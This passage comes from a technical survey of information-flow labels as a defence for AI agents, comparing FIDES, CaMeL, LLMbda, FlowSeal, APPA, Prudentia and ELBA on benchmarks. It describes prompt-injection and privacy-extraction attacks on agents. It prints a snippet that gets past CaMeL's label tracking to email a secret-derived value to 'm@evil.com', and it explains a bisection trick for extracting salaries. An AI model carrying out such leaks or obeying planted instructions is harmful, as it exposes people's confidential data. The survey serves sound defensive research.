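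The perfect privacy score is also weaker evidence than it looks. The benchmark counts leaks by searching for the same protected strings that the final check removes, so the score has to be 1.000 if the check runs correctly. If a protected salary is "184,000" and the model writes "a hundred and eighty-four thousand", the check won't remove it and the benchmark won't count it as a leak.

The gains in utility are more convincing, because the string check never blocked a reply to an authorised user, so utility depended on the separate calls. The size of the gains is uncertain because DeepSeek-V4-Pro's single-agent utility was 0.597 here but 78.2% in Yang and colleagues' own tests, which used a different model to play the users. Measured against that figure, the improvement would be about half as large. The separate calls also use many more tokens, although in the DeepSeek test the system finished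 11% faster because the calls ran in parallel.

The fixed refusal also reveals that the resource and its authorized list exist, since it ends with "You don't appear to be on the authorized list for this resource". The planning model's instructions include a nearly identical explanation as an example of what not to write, because it "leaks the list."

Like Muses-Bench, Harness-MU checks each reply against the permissions of one user. If the finance chief asks about salaries, the reply passes because she is allowed to read them. If the agent then posts that reply in the channel, the analyst and the contractor can read it too. To prevent this, the code would have to check the reply against the permissions of everyone in V and look for more than exact string matches.

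## How can restrictions on data follow it through a language model?

Harness-MU's final check would miss a salary written out in words because it only compares strings. Information-flow control instead tracks where data came from. When an agent reads something, the software around the model labels it with who may read it and how much to trust its source. Anything the model writes afterwards gets a label computed from the labels of its inputs, so rewording the salary doesn't change who may receive it.

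### Labels and how they combine

The theory comes largely from military computing. In the early 1970s, David Bell and Leonard LaPadula described a system that held documents at several levels of secrecy. One of their rules stops users from reading documents above their clearance. Another, called "no write down", stops a program with access to secret documents from writing to a less secret file, even if its user may edit that file. This second rule is needed because the program could contain hidden code that copies the secret, even if the user is honest.

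In 1977, Kenneth Biba reversed the model to protect data from tampering instead of disclosure. Under his rules, unreliable data must not influence reliable data. In one version, a program's trust level drops to that of the least reliable data it has read. An agent that opened the subcontractor's email would drop in the same way.

Dorothy Denning's *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976) supplies the mathematics that agent systems now use for both kinds of rule. Denning orders labels by a relation ⊑, read as "may flow to". Public data may flow to a secret file, so public ⊑ secret, but not the other way round. Any two labels a and b have a join, written a ⊔ b, which is the least restrictive label that both may flow to. Data computed from inputs labeled a and b gets the label a ⊔ b. An ordered set with these joins is a (semi-)lattice.

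This suits an agent because one label can describe the whole context, however many messages it contains. The join is the same whatever order the agent reads the messages in, and rereading a message doesn't change it.

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, apply this to agents with a pair of labels:

- **Confidentiality** can simply be public or secret, but it can also be a reader set, the list of people who may read the data. The join of two reader sets is their intersection, since only someone who may read both sources may read a text based on both.
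- **Integrity** can be trusted or untrusted. Trusted data may flow into an untrusted text, so trusted ⊑ untrusted, and anything based partly on untrusted data is untrusted. A more detailed version lists everyone who could have written the data, and its join is the union of those lists.

Restrictions therefore only accumulate. Each new source can remove readers from the context label or make it untrusted, but no source can add a reader or restore trust.

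### Label, propagate, check

Microsoft divides the work into three steps:

1. Label every piece of data when it reaches the agent.
2. Propagate the labels to everything the agent derives from the data.
3. Check the labels before each tool call, then allow the call, block it or ask a person.

The second step is difficult with a language model because the software can't determine which parts of the context influenced an output. Costa and colleagues take the cautious option of giving each model output the join of the labels of everything the model received, including the tool descriptions. A tool's result gets the join of the labels of the call, the inputs and whatever the tool read. Anything the tool writes gets this label too, so a secret saved to a file is still labeled secret when the agent reads the file later.

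Suppose the construction firm's agent uses a mail tool that lists a message's sender and recipients as its permitted readers and marks only mail from inside the firm as trusted. The context label then changes as the agent reads messages.

| The agent adds to its context | Integrity of the context | Who may read what it writes |
|---|---|---|
| The employee's request | Trusted | Anyone |
| A site report sent to the employee, the manager and the colleague | Trusted | Employee, manager, colleague |
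| The colleague's confidential message to the employee | Trusted | Employee, colleague |
| The subcontractor's email to the employee and the manager | Untrusted | Employee |

When the agent opens the colleague's message, the software removes the manager from the reader set. It can then block a summary that mentions a new site engineer without understanding that this reveals a resignation. But it would also block a summary that never mentions the colleague, because both summaries carry the same label. The next section covers ways to make labels less restrictive.

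The subcontractor can't change the email's label by hiding a line that tells the model the email comes from the chief executive, because the software sets the label from the email's source and doesn't take instructions from its text.

Two basic policies determine what the third step allows. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, a later paper on the same approach, call them "trusted action" and "permitted flow":

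- **Trusted action:** the agent may take a consequential action only if the decision to take it came from a trusted context. Some inputs, such as a recipient's address, may also have to be trusted.
- **Permitted flow:** the agent may send data only if every recipient may read it. If S is the reader set of the data and R is the set of recipients, this means R ⊆ S.

Permitted flow is the test Liu applies to a group chat, except that S now belongs to text the agent wrote rather than to a stored document.

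Each policy prevents a failure that the other allows. As Costa and colleagues point out, permitted flow alone doesn't stop prompt injection, although it limits the damage. The subcontractor's line could still make the agent cancel the site meeting, because cancelling it reveals nothing. Trusted action would prevent the cancellation, but it wouldn't stop the agent from disclosing the resignation if the agent had read only internal mail.

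### Alex, Priya and Marco

Microsoft illustrates permitted flow with a leak that involves no attacker. Alex asks an agent to answer the mail in his inbox. Priya has sent him a preview of the quarterly sales figures. Marco, who isn't authorised to see the figures yet, has also written because he is curious about them. The agent reads both emails and drafts a helpful reply to Marco that discloses the figures.

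Priya's email has the reader set {Alex, Priya}, and Marco's has {Alex, Marco}. The draft draws on a context that holds both, so its reader set is

{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}.

Marco isn't in the set, so the agent may not send him the reply automatically. If Priya had copied Marco into her email, the calculation would be

{Alex, Priya, Marco} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex, Marco},

and the reply could go out without anyone's approval.

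An ordinary permission check would have allowed the first reply, since Alex may read both emails and write to Marco. The labels stop it, and they also cover a paraphrase such as "you'll be pleased with the quarter", which contains no figures.

However, the labels don't show whether the draft contains anything from Priya. If the agent had written only "Sorry, I can't discuss this yet", the draft would still have the reader set {Alex}. A thank-you note to Priya would have the same problem, because the context also contains Marco's email. Microsoft's design lets the software ask Alex in such cases, and the prompt can list the people who would gain access to the information.

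Microsoft also applies the labels to the GitHub attack that Invariant Labs demonstrated. The issue on the public repository is labeled untrusted, and the code in the private repository is labeled private. An agent that has read both may not post publicly, but one that works only on public repositories, or only on private ones, can finish its task unattended. This avoids Invariant's limit of one repository per session. Microsoft suggests treating a link to an unapproved host as a public channel. This would also help with the Slack previews and the answers that made Copilot contact an outside server.

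### A published policy that lets mistakes through

Microsoft has published a sample policy for a tool that posts messages to a Teams channel. It fetches the channel's member list and makes its decision in this order:

1. If the context is trusted, send the message.
2. Otherwise, if every channel member may read the content, send the message.
3. Otherwise, ask the user, and list the people who would gain access.

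(The code ends with a fourth branch that refuses the message, but the agent should never reach it. The branch before it applies whenever the number of unauthorised members is zero or more.)

The order matters because a trusted context settles the decision before the policy uses the reader set. The table compares the sample with two policies, one that tests only the readers and one that requires both a trusted context and permitted readers. It assumes that each prompts the user when its test fails.

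| Context | May all members read it? | Sample policy | Readers only | Both required |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Trusted | Yes | Send | Send | Send |
| Trusted | No | Send | Ask | Ask |
| Untrusted | Yes | Send | Send | Ask |
| Untrusted | No | Ask | Ask | Ask |

Suppose the finance chief asks about the compensation budget in a shared channel, and the agent reads the salary file from a trusted internal database. The sample policy lets the agent post the salaries to everyone, even though their label allows only the chief to read them.

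The policy would give an odd result for the construction firm's summary. If the subcontractor emails that week, his message makes the context untrusted, so the software compares readers and catches the resignation. But when all the mail is internal, the context is trusted and the summary goes to the manager without that comparison.

The sample deliberately follows a rule that Microsoft calls "robust declassification", which means that injected text can't cause the release of restricted data. Kolluri and colleagues use the same rule in their tests, where a tool that sends data out has to satisfy either the trusted action or the permitted flow condition. Costa and colleagues reason that if nobody could have tampered with the context, a release to new readers "can be assumed to be intentional".

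That assumption is reasonable for a person who clicks "share" but weak for an agent. Alex may have wanted his mail answered without meaning to give Marco the sales figures. Costa and colleagues themselves note that models misread users' intentions even when all the data is trusted. Microsoft also recommends assuming that a model error could trigger any action an agent can take for its user.

The sample therefore protects against an attacker's instruction but not against the agent's own error. If both emails in Microsoft's example counted as trusted internal mail, the same rule in a mail tool would let the agent send the figures to Marco. A firm that wants to prevent this should compare readers in every context and ask the user when the agent is about to share something more widely.

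### What software supports labels

Microsoft and GitHub have built this approach into several products and prototypes. The table gives their status as Microsoft described it in mid-2026.

| Software | What it adds | Status |
|---|---|---|
| MCP metadata | Fields for labels and policies | Microsoft's convention, with a proposal to the MCP community planned |
| GitHub MCP server | Labels on the results of tools | Optional feature |
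| GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent for the command line | A context label and checks on selected GitHub tools | Experimental, off by default |
| Microsoft Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents | Labels, policy checks and ways to hide untrusted text | Experimental, Python only |
| MCP gateway | Labels and policies for servers that lack them | Open-source prototype |

The Model Context Protocol already lets clients and servers attach extra metadata to tool calls and results. Microsoft puts the labels in this metadata, so software that doesn't support them can ignore them. A label can cover a whole result or a single field. In Microsoft's example, a call to the Teams tool is labeled untrusted as a whole, but its message text is labeled trusted and has two permitted readers. Servers can publish their policies in the same way.

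For each tool on a new server, a developer has to describe the structure of its results, write a function that computes their labels, and write or choose a policy. Microsoft suggests a rougher alternative based on hints that many tools already provide. The client could always allow tools that only read from a closed system, require public inputs for tools that read from the open web, and ask the user before any destructive action.

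The GitHub server labels files and issues from public repositories as public and untrusted, and those from private repositories as private and trusted. Labeling everything in private repositories as trusted is lenient, since a contractor with access could plant an instruction there. A policy like the Teams sample would then treat that instruction as trusted and skip the comparison of readers. A code change by the GitHub developer gokhanarkan is stricter for searches across repositories. It labels every issue in the results as untrusted, because users write issues, and joins the confidentiality labels of all the repositories involved.

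Labels from the server have no effect unless something checks them. pkg.go.dev's *ifc* (2026) lists a package from May that defines these labels and, according to its description, leaves enforcement to a separate service. The package isn't in the latest version of its module, so developers should check whether it has moved before using it. On the client side, Copilot CLI updates its context label after every tool result. When Microsoft described its checks, they covered only some of GitHub's tools and no other MCP servers, so a label on a mail server's result would not have protected that result in Copilot CLI.

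Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) announced the Agent Framework version of FIDES on 20 May. This version takes its name from the system in Costa and colleagues' paper, but its standard labels are simpler. Microsoft's documentation lists three confidentiality levels: public, private and "user identity", which covers personal data and credentials. A developer sets the highest level that each tool that sends data can accept.

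These levels can keep private code out of a public comment, but they can't express the restriction in the example with Alex, Priya and Marco, because both emails would be private and a mail tool that accepts private data would send the reply to Marco. A developer who needs to distinguish between colleagues has to use reader sets, which Microsoft's gateway supports.

If a tool's output has no label, the framework treats it as untrusted and public. This default protects integrity, since unlabelled text can't drive a tool that refuses untrusted contexts, but it doesn't protect confidentiality, because the framework treats an unlabelled secret as public. Microsoft's documentation says that a forgotten label therefore "fails closed", which is true only for integrity.

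In the documentation's example, a malicious issue contains instructions for an agent to read a file of credentials and post the contents as a comment. The framework stops the comment because the file is labeled private and the commenting tool accepts only public data. If the developer had forgotten to label the file, this limit would not have stopped the comment.

### What the labels guarantee

The software checks the labels outside the model, so the check runs regardless of what the model writes. If the labels and policies are correct, nothing the agent writes can override a refusal. Costa and colleagues prove a more precise property called explicit secrecy, which is weaker than the noninterference described earlier.

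Suppose an agent follows the same sequence of steps on two versions of its stored data that differ only in their secrets. Explicit secrecy requires the public parts of the two versions to still match afterward. This rules out copying a secret into a public message, directly or through intermediate files.

Explicit secrecy doesn't cover the agent's choice of steps. Suppose the agent has a tool that refreshes the firm's public vacancies page and takes no inputs. The agent learns from the colleague's message that a job will soon be open, so it refreshes the page. The refresh does the same thing whatever the message says, so explicit secrecy holds. But someone who sees the page change may guess that a person is leaving. Permitted flow doesn't prevent this either, because the call contains no text whose reader set could be compared.

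Security researchers call this an indirect or implicit flow. Costa and colleagues accept it because, once the agent had read a secret, full noninterference would block nearly every tool with a publicly visible effect. They note that older systems for phones and web browsers made the same compromise. Their model also leaves out timing and the size of network messages, and it assumes the language model always gives the same answer to the same input.

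A context label catches some leaks that happen without copying. The scheduling assistant's offer inherits the calendar's reader set whether it is for slot 10 or slot 11, so an outside recipient would get neither offer without approval. The label prevents the leak by blocking all such offers, including harmless ones.

### A proof that includes the model's own code

*The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) aims to close the gap left by explicit secrecy. LLMbda is a small programming language for agents. It has commands to send a message to a model, receive a reply, copy a conversation and clear it. A model's reply can be a program, which LLMbda then runs. Every value has a label, and so does the conversation.

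They motivate the language with a flaw in CaMeL, an earlier system in which a model writes a program for each task and the software tracks labels as the program runs. CaMeL refuses to send an email inside a branch that depends on a secret bank balance. But a program can get around this with a trick that dates from 1974. A simplified version looks like this:

```python
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
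if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line changes `tmp` to false and labels it secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so `rich` stays true and keeps its public label, and the last line sends the email. If the balance is low, the third line does nothing, the fourth changes `rich` to false, and no email goes out. In both cases `rich` is labelled public, although its value reveals whether the balance is above the threshold. The label tracker misses this leak because it updates a label only when the program changes the variable.

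LLMbda also tracks the secrets that influenced the program's current branch, and it protects the conversation as it would a variable. After a choice that depends on a secret, the program stops if it tries to add to a public conversation. This keeps the addition from revealing the secret, but the stop itself can reveal something, since the program may stop for one value of the secret and continue for another.

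Garby and colleagues therefore prove a version of noninterference that allows for programs that stop or never finish. Suppose two starting states look the same to an observer. Let μ(q) and ν(q) be the probabilities that the program finishes with result q, as the observer sees it, from each state. The theorem says that there is a single function ω, with total probability at most 1, such that

μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and ν(q) ≤ ω(q) for every q.

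If the program always finishes from both states, the two sets of probabilities must be identical, so the observer learns nothing about the secret. If it sometimes fails to finish, the probabilities can differ, but half the sum of their differences over all results is at most the average of the two states' chances of not finishing. For example, if the program fails to finish in 2% of runs from one state and 4% from the other, half the sum is at most 3 percentage points.

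That limit applies to a single run. The paper points out that CaMeL retries failed programs in a loop that its label tracker doesn't cover. An attacker who can see whether each attempt failed could use the retries to extract a secret one bit at a time. LLMbda runs the agent's loop inside the language, so the labels carry over from one attempt to the next.

The proof covers every program in LLMbda, including any that the language model writes. Lean, a proof-checking program, has verified each step. The software that runs the agents is also written in Lean, and the theorems apply directly to it. The proof is much stronger evidence than a test, because no prompt can produce a counterexample within the proof's formal model.

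This is consistent with the earlier result that a monitor watching one run can't catch such leaks, because that result covers only monitors that never raise a false alarm. LLMbda stops some harmless runs too.

#### What the proof assumes

The theorem treats all tools and data sources as parts of the program, but a real mail server is outside the program. Garby and colleagues acknowledge this limitation. They also assume that the model's replies follow fixed probabilities that depend only on the conversation. A provider that let one customer's conversation influence another's replies would break this assumption.

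Someone still has to label the data correctly and put a check in front of every sensitive tool. If the mail tool wrongly marks the colleague's message as readable by the manager, the resignation will still leak to the manager even though the proof holds.

Programs can also mark untrusted data as trusted with a command called "endorse". An agent may need to do this, for example, to pay a bill it reads in a file. The theorem shows that endorsing data can't turn a secret into public information, but a bad endorsement can still lead the agent to send money to an attacker.

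#### What the tests add

Garby and colleagues built an agent called Randori in LLMbda and tested it on the banking tasks from AgentDojo. They ran each of the 144 combinations of 16 tasks and 9 attacks three times on each of three models, for a total of 1,296 runs. Two attacks succeeded. In both, the task required the agent to read a file and make the payment described in it, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents.

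The low attack rate is weak evidence that labels help, though. In 97 of the 144 combinations, the attack needed a tool call that the program written for the user's task would never contain. Writing the program before reading any untrusted data is enough to stop most of these. In the other 47, even CaMeL with its policy checks switched off resisted the attack in all 141 completed runs on GPT-5.2 and 138 of 141 on MiMo-v2.5. Better evidence would require attacks that usually succeed without labels.

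The tests are more informative about usefulness. With GPT-5.2 and no attacks, Randori completed 36 of 48 runs, while CaMeL completed 32 with its policy checks off and 18 with them on. Randori therefore seems to avoid much of the drop in completed runs that enforcement usually causes, but it applied only a subset of CaMeL's policies, so the results aren't fully comparable. Removing Randori's ability to endorse data reduced completed runs from 36 to 30 on Qwen3.7-plus and from 31 to 26 on MiMo-v2.5.

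### Tracking individual records

A context label can't distinguish a summary that mentions the resignation from one that doesn't. Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) try to make this distinction in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* by tracking individual records and comparing them with the agent's output.

They begin with attacks on agents that rely on prompts to protect privacy. In their main scenario, Jane's agent holds Mark's mental health diagnosis, and his former wife Emily wants it. The defence is a detailed prompt that tells the agent to check who is asking and get Mark's consent whenever someone requests information. Emily has three ways around it:

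- She invites Jane to fill in her part of a shared document, which looks like ordinary teamwork and not a request for information.
- She makes a list of true and false facts about Mark and asks Jane to delete the wrong ones. The agent writes nothing sensitive, but the entries it leaves are the true ones.
- She asks for a one-word reply by email, while a shared page tells the agent to write the details there.

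These work because the model has to recognise that it is making a privacy decision before it can follow the prompt, and Emily controls how the request looks. None of them needs a hidden instruction to ignore the rules.

Shim and colleagues' defence, FlowSeal, moves the decision to the point where data leaves:

1. The data's owner, or software that reads existing permissions, registers each sensitive record with its text, its owner and the people who may receive it.
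2. When the agent reads something, code outside the model compares the result with the registered records and notes which ones the agent has seen.
3. If the agent combines records in a summary, the summary inherits the restrictions of all of them.
4. When the agent tries to write or share, the code checks the recipient. It allows approved recipients and blocks banned ones.
5. For anyone else, a separate model receives only the protected records and the proposed output. It answers "safe" or "blocked".

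The separate model never receives Emily's account of why she needs the text. FlowSeal also gives the agent tools to ask the owner for consent, but the code checks every outgoing call even if the agent does not use those tools.

In 105 scenarios with three runs each, Shim and colleagues measured the share of sensitive items that leaked.

| Attack | Detailed privacy prompt | FlowSeal |
|---|---|---|
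| Shared document | 52.2% | 0.5% |
| Deleting false entries | 75.6% | 2.3% |
| Split between email and a shared page | 43.8% | 2.2% |

(In one passage, the paper gives 38.5% for the last attack against the prompt, but its results table and introduction support 43.8%.)

The improvement is large, and it held when the researchers changed the agent's model in the shared-document test. They also tried the deletion attack on real Gmail and Notion accounts, where an existing privacy checker leaked 34.7% of the items and FlowSeal leaked none. They counted only facts that appeared word for word in Notion, so they could have missed paraphrased leaks.

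In Costa and colleagues' system, a policy engine outside the language model checks the labels before each call, so Shim and colleagues are wrong to say that the system leaves enforcement to the model and would therefore be vulnerable to these attacks. With reader sets and a strict permitted-flow policy, an agent that had opened Mark's record could not edit a page that Emily can read. The system differs from Shim and colleagues' in that a context label would also block harmless edits.

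FlowSeal's precision comes with a weaker guarantee. Under its theorem, nothing derived from a protected record reaches an unauthorised recipient unless the separate model wrongly answers "safe". Shim and colleagues acknowledge that paraphrases can cause this error. They also exclude prompt injection, so the tests don't show what would happen if an attacker got the agent to include instructions to the separate model in its output. FlowSeal protects only registered records, so someone must register the colleague's message before the agent reads it.

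FlowSeal can also be too cautious. In another test, the owners agreed to share their data whenever the agent asked. Agents with the privacy prompts delivered 61% to 67% of the requested items, while FlowSeal delivered 33%, mainly because its agent asked for consent less often.

Shim and colleagues then replaced the separate model with a fixed answer to see how much depended on that model. "Leaked" refers to the shared-document attack.

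| Answer for unknown recipients | Leaked | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| The separate model decides | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| Always "blocked" | 1.3% | 0% |
| Always "safe" | 24.9% | 79.4% |

With "always blocked", FlowSeal behaves much like a strict context label and no longer depends on a model's judgement. It completed no harmless tasks because every recipient in the test was unknown and the data owners ignored all requests for permission.

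## How can an agent stay useful once its context is restricted?

A context label only gets stricter as the agent reads, so an agent that reads enough may end up unable to act on what it has learned. Suppose the construction firm's employee asks her agent to check Thursday's weather, move the site meeting if it will rain, and tell the attendees. The firm requires a trusted context for any action that changes something, and information may go only to people allowed to read it.

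| The agent reads | Trust | Who may read what it writes | What it can still do without approval |
|---|---|---|---|
| The request | Trusted | Anyone | Everything |
| The meeting entry, shared by the employee, manager, colleague and subcontractor | Trusted | Those four | Move the meeting, write to the four |
| The employee's private calendar, to find another slot | Trusted | Employee | Change her private calendar |
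| A public weather page | Untrusted | Employee | Answer the employee |

The agent now knows when to move the meeting but isn't allowed to move it, even though the weather page is probably harmless. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls this problem "label explosion".

To stay useful, an agent has to keep restrictive data out of its context, or someone with authority has to make an exception. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev et al., 2026) proves that once a label blocks a call for lack of trust or permitted readers, no further reading can unblock it. With four people and two levels of trust, the label can tighten at most 4 + 2 − 1 = 5 times, and then it stays the same.

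An agent can also redo the work with less data. Costa and colleagues describe a method that looks for the messages that influenced an output and generates the output again from those alone. If the employee's weekly summary doesn't need the colleague's confidential message, the agent can rewrite it from the other thirty-nine, and the manager can receive it. This requires extra model calls and only works if the output doesn't need the restricted source.

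### Two models, one without tools

Willison proposed the dual-model pattern in 2023. One model, the planner, can use tools but never sees untrusted text. A second, quarantined model reads the untrusted text but has no tools. Ordinary software stores the text in variables and shows the planner only the variable names.

Suppose the employee asks the agent to summarise her three latest emails and send the summary to Bob:

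1. The planner calls the mail tool. The software stores the emails as `#emails` and gives the planner that name.
2. The planner asks the quarantined model to summarise `#emails`. The software stores the answer as `#summary`.
3. The planner calls the messaging tool with Bob's address and `#summary`. The software inserts the text just before sending.

A hidden instruction in an email can't change the recipient, because the model that chose Bob never read the email, but the instruction can still change the summary. Costa and colleagues give the example of an email that tells the quarantined model to return an empty summary. The variables also need labels, since the pattern alone doesn't check whether Bob is allowed to read the emails.

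This works when the planner can fix the steps in advance. Let T(d) be the set of call sequences that complete a task when the stored data is d. Costa and colleagues call a task data-independent if at least one sequence works for all possible data:

⋂ T(d) ≠ ∅, taken over every possible d.

The summary for Bob qualifies, because the same three calls work whatever the emails contain. "If one of my emails asks for a meeting, put it in my calendar" is data-dependent, because the agent should call the calendar tool only if an email asks for a meeting.

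### CaMeL writes the whole program first

CaMeL completely separates planning from reading. The planner writes a program for the entire task from the user's request, before the agent reads any data. An interpreter then runs the program, passes text to the quarantined model where the program calls for it, and checks the policy before each tool call.

The planner finishes its work before the subcontractor's hidden line arrives, so the line may change a value in the program but can't add a step. However, the planner also can't react to surprises. If an attachment turns out to need a password that is in the next email, the program will fail unless the planner foresaw this.

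### FIDES hides only what would add a restriction

FIDES, the system from Costa and colleagues' paper, is more flexible. When a tool returns a result, it compares the label of each field with the label of the context. It puts any field that would make the context more restricted into a variable and shows the planner the rest. The planner might see an email's date, for example, but not its subject or body.

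If the planner needs to know what a variable contains, it can open the variable and accept the restriction, or it can ask the quarantined model a question and limit the answer to a fixed format. The software enforces the format while the model generates the answer, so a yes-or-no question can only produce "yes" or "no". The meeting request then works like this:

1. The planner fetches the emails, which go into a variable.
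2. It asks the quarantined model whether any email requests a meeting, with the answer limited to yes or no.
3. It opens the answer, which is "yes".
4. It asks the quarantined model for the details of the meeting, which go into another variable.
5. It calls the calendar tool with that variable.

Strictly speaking, the context is untrusted after step 3, because the "yes" came from an untrusted email. FIDES therefore records the answer's format in the label, so that a firm can write a policy that allows an untrusted yes or no but not untrusted free text. Costa and colleagues reason that a single bit is unlikely to carry a prompt injection. They left fixed-format answers out of the version they tested because most tasks in their benchmark didn't need them.

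A one-word answer can still be false, even though it can't contain an instruction. Suppose the agent checks an outside email to see whether the scaffolding passed its inspection, then tells the crew they can climb it. The sender can get the crew to climb unsafe scaffolding by falsely reporting that it passed. In the calendar example, the sender also chooses the date and the participants.

Kravchenko and colleagues point out that checking an answer's format limits its shape and size but does not establish that it is true. Their system treats the answer as untrusted unless the firm has explicitly decided otherwise. That seems the right default, because the firm can first consider what would happen if the answer were a lie. It might rely on a weather page to move a meeting, but it should get the scaffolding result from the inspector's own records.

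Short answers can also reveal secrets. If an agent will say whether the director earns more than a given amount, a user can find any salary below $262,144 to the nearest dollar with 18 questions, because each answer can halve the remaining range and 2¹⁸ = 262,144. A firm that allows such answers about restricted data also has to limit their number.

### Planning around the rules, and making exceptions

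To move the site meeting, the agent needs two exceptions, endorsement and declassification. Endorsement is an authorised decision to let less trusted data influence a protected action, such as letting the weather page's forecast decide whether the meeting moves. Declassification is an authorised decision to release restricted data to more people, such as telling the other three that the employee is free on Friday morning. Verifying a source isn't enough to justify endorsement. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* notes that a signature proves where a document came from but not that it is safe or correct.

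Kolluri and colleagues built Prudentia on top of FIDES to reduce the number of exceptions an agent needs. FIDES doesn't show its planner which calls the policy will block, so the planner may open a variable unnecessarily and lose the ability to act. Prudentia adds the rules to the tool descriptions and gives the planner information about the labels. Before opening a variable, the planner is supposed to explain why it needs the text and list the calls it plans to make next.

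The planner can then ask the user to endorse the text, which keeps the context trusted, or open it without asking. Kolluri and colleagues give the example of an email with ten to-do items that each require a protected action. Endorsing the email replaces ten separate approvals with one decision. If no protected action will follow, the planner can skip the request. In one run, the user wanted a summary of her appointments and a link to reset her password, and the agent opened the untrusted text without asking because it only had to reply to her.

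Endorsement saves time but gives the user fewer chances to notice an attack. If someone has added an eleventh item to the email, the agent will carry it out with the others, whereas a separate prompt for each action would have shown it to the user. She therefore has to check the whole email before endorsing it, and the endorsement prompt has to show her any hidden text.

Prudentia requires the user to approve each call that declassifies private information, because Kolluri and colleagues think the decision depends too much on the situation for a shortcut. An approval in APPA also covers only one exact call, and it leaves the label unchanged. A fixed rule, a person or another model can give the approval, within limits the firm has set. If the employee lets the agent send her manager one restricted summary, the agent needs a new approval to send the next.

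### Reading in a separate branch

APPA lets an agent read untrusted data in a temporary copy of the conversation. In Kravchenko and colleagues' example, a support agent has to extract a few facts from a public issue tracker and then update an internal database:

1. The main conversation fixes the form of the answer in advance, here a ticket number plus a severity and a component from set lists.
2. The software copies the conversation into a branch, which starts with the same label. With a fresh label, the branch could release secrets the agent had already read.
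3. The branch reads the web page, and its label becomes untrusted.
4. The branch returns its answer. The software rejects free text or anything else in the wrong form, then discards the branch's conversation.
5. The main conversation continues and can update the database, provided the firm's policy treats such an answer as trusted.

Discarding the branch doesn't undo its actions, so any email it sent stays sent.

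Before a call runs, APPA also checks how it would change the context's label. One tool in its tests reads a confidential ledger and emails it outside the company in a single call. APPA blocks this call based on the label the context would have after the read. Checking only the current label would allow the call, because the agent hasn't read the ledger yet.

*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) describes ELBA, a system that builds similar protections out of an existing programming language, Haskell. The agent must write its steps in Haskell, and ELBA checks each program before running it. Haskell's types can specify what kind of data a function accepts and what effects a program may have. In the paper's bibliography example, the function that writes to the file accepts only entries of type `Trusted Bib`, which the agent can get only by fetching them from DBLP,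 a database of computer science papers. The agent can sort and filter these entries freely, but ELBA rejects any program that tries to write an invented one.

An ELBA program can read untrusted data by calling a sub-agent that has a separate label. The sub-agent can use tools within the limits of that label, unlike the quarantined model in the dual-model pattern, which can't use tools. It can also write a new program after seeing the data, so ELBA, unlike CaMeL, doesn't need a complete plan in advance.

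### What the tests show

Researchers have tested most of these systems on AgentDojo, which simulates an office, a travel service, a bank and a Slack workspace. It has 97 user tasks and 36 attacker goals. Testers measure how many tasks an agent completes, then plant instructions in the data and count how often the agent carries out the attacker's goal. AgentDojo has no labels of its own, so Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks used it.

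The paper's 2025 results with GPT-4o are now mainly of historical interest. It reports that attacks succeeded 152 times against a basic agent, 21 times against FIDES with its policy checks off, and never against either agent with the checks on. With checks on, FIDES completed an average of 50.0% of tasks across the four environments, compared with 41.9% for the basic agent. The paper calls this gain 8%, but it is 8 percentage points. With OpenAI's o1 model the gain was 16, presumably also in percentage points. With checks off, FIDES's completion rate was lower than the basic agent's by 23.7 points with GPT-4o and 6.3 points with o1.

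Kolluri and colleagues later ran AgentDojo with GPT-5 and counted user approvals. Their basic agent asks the user before every consequential action, as many coding assistants do, while the other agents ask only when a call breaks the policy. The counts are totals for the tasks each agent completed, averaged over five runs.

| Agent, with GPT-5 | Completed with unlimited approvals | Completed with no approvals | Approvals needed |
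|---|---|---|---|
| Basic | 72.3% | 35.1% | 52.0 |
| Basic with labels | 72.3% | 43.4% | 40.4 |
| FIDES | 78.9% | 57.1% | 41.3 |
| Prudentia | 80.0% | 72.7% | 7.3 |

Prudentia completed about as many tasks without any approvals as the basic agent did with unlimited approvals. Kolluri and colleagues argue that earlier studies overstated the drawbacks of labels because they compared a protected agent that could never ask for approval with an unprotected one that never had to. Their argument is convincing for a firm that would otherwise review every action, but the unprotected agent is still the relevant comparison for someone who has already clicked "Always Allow".

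Prudentia depends on a capable model. With GPT-4o, it completed 42.5% of tasks without approvals, compared with 50.3% for FIDES. It also uses far more input tokens. On the banking tasks with GPT-4o, it averaged about 22,600, against 7,700 for FIDES and 1,000 for the basic agent with labels. Each task cost 3.9 cents with Prudentia, 1.5 cents with FIDES and 0.4 cents with the basic agent. Kolluri and colleagues hadn't yet tried to reduce this overhead.

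Zhou and colleagues tested ELBA and CaMeL with newer models, but only on AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks. The table shows how many tasks each system completed when there was no attack.

| Model | CaMeL, checks off | CaMeL, checks on | ELBA, checks off | ELBA, checks on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 15 | 5 | 18 | 10 |
| Opus 4.8 | 16 | 6 | 16 | 9 |
| GPT 5.4 | 17 | 5 | 16 | 10 |
| Sonnet 5 | 13 | 4 | 14 | 8 |

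Turning on the checks lowered task completion by 43 to 57 percentage points for CaMeL and 29 to 38 for ELBA, so enforcement still causes large losses on these tasks, even with better models. With so few tasks and one attempt at each, a difference of one or two tasks means little. But ELBA's lead over CaMeL with checks on also held under attack: with Opus 4.7 and one type of attack, ELBA completed 52 of 105 runs and CaMeL completed 24. ELBA took about three times as long, and the CaMeL results come from the developers of a rival system.

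None of the attacks worked on any of these models, even with the checks off, so AgentDojo's standard attacks can no longer be used to test whether a defence helps. Zhou and colleagues don't conclude that the models are safe, because OpenAI's automated attacker, GPT-Red, consistently got past GPT-5.5's defences. So they simulated a sub-agent that always obeys the attacker by replacing its whole prompt with the attacker's text whenever it received a planted instruction.

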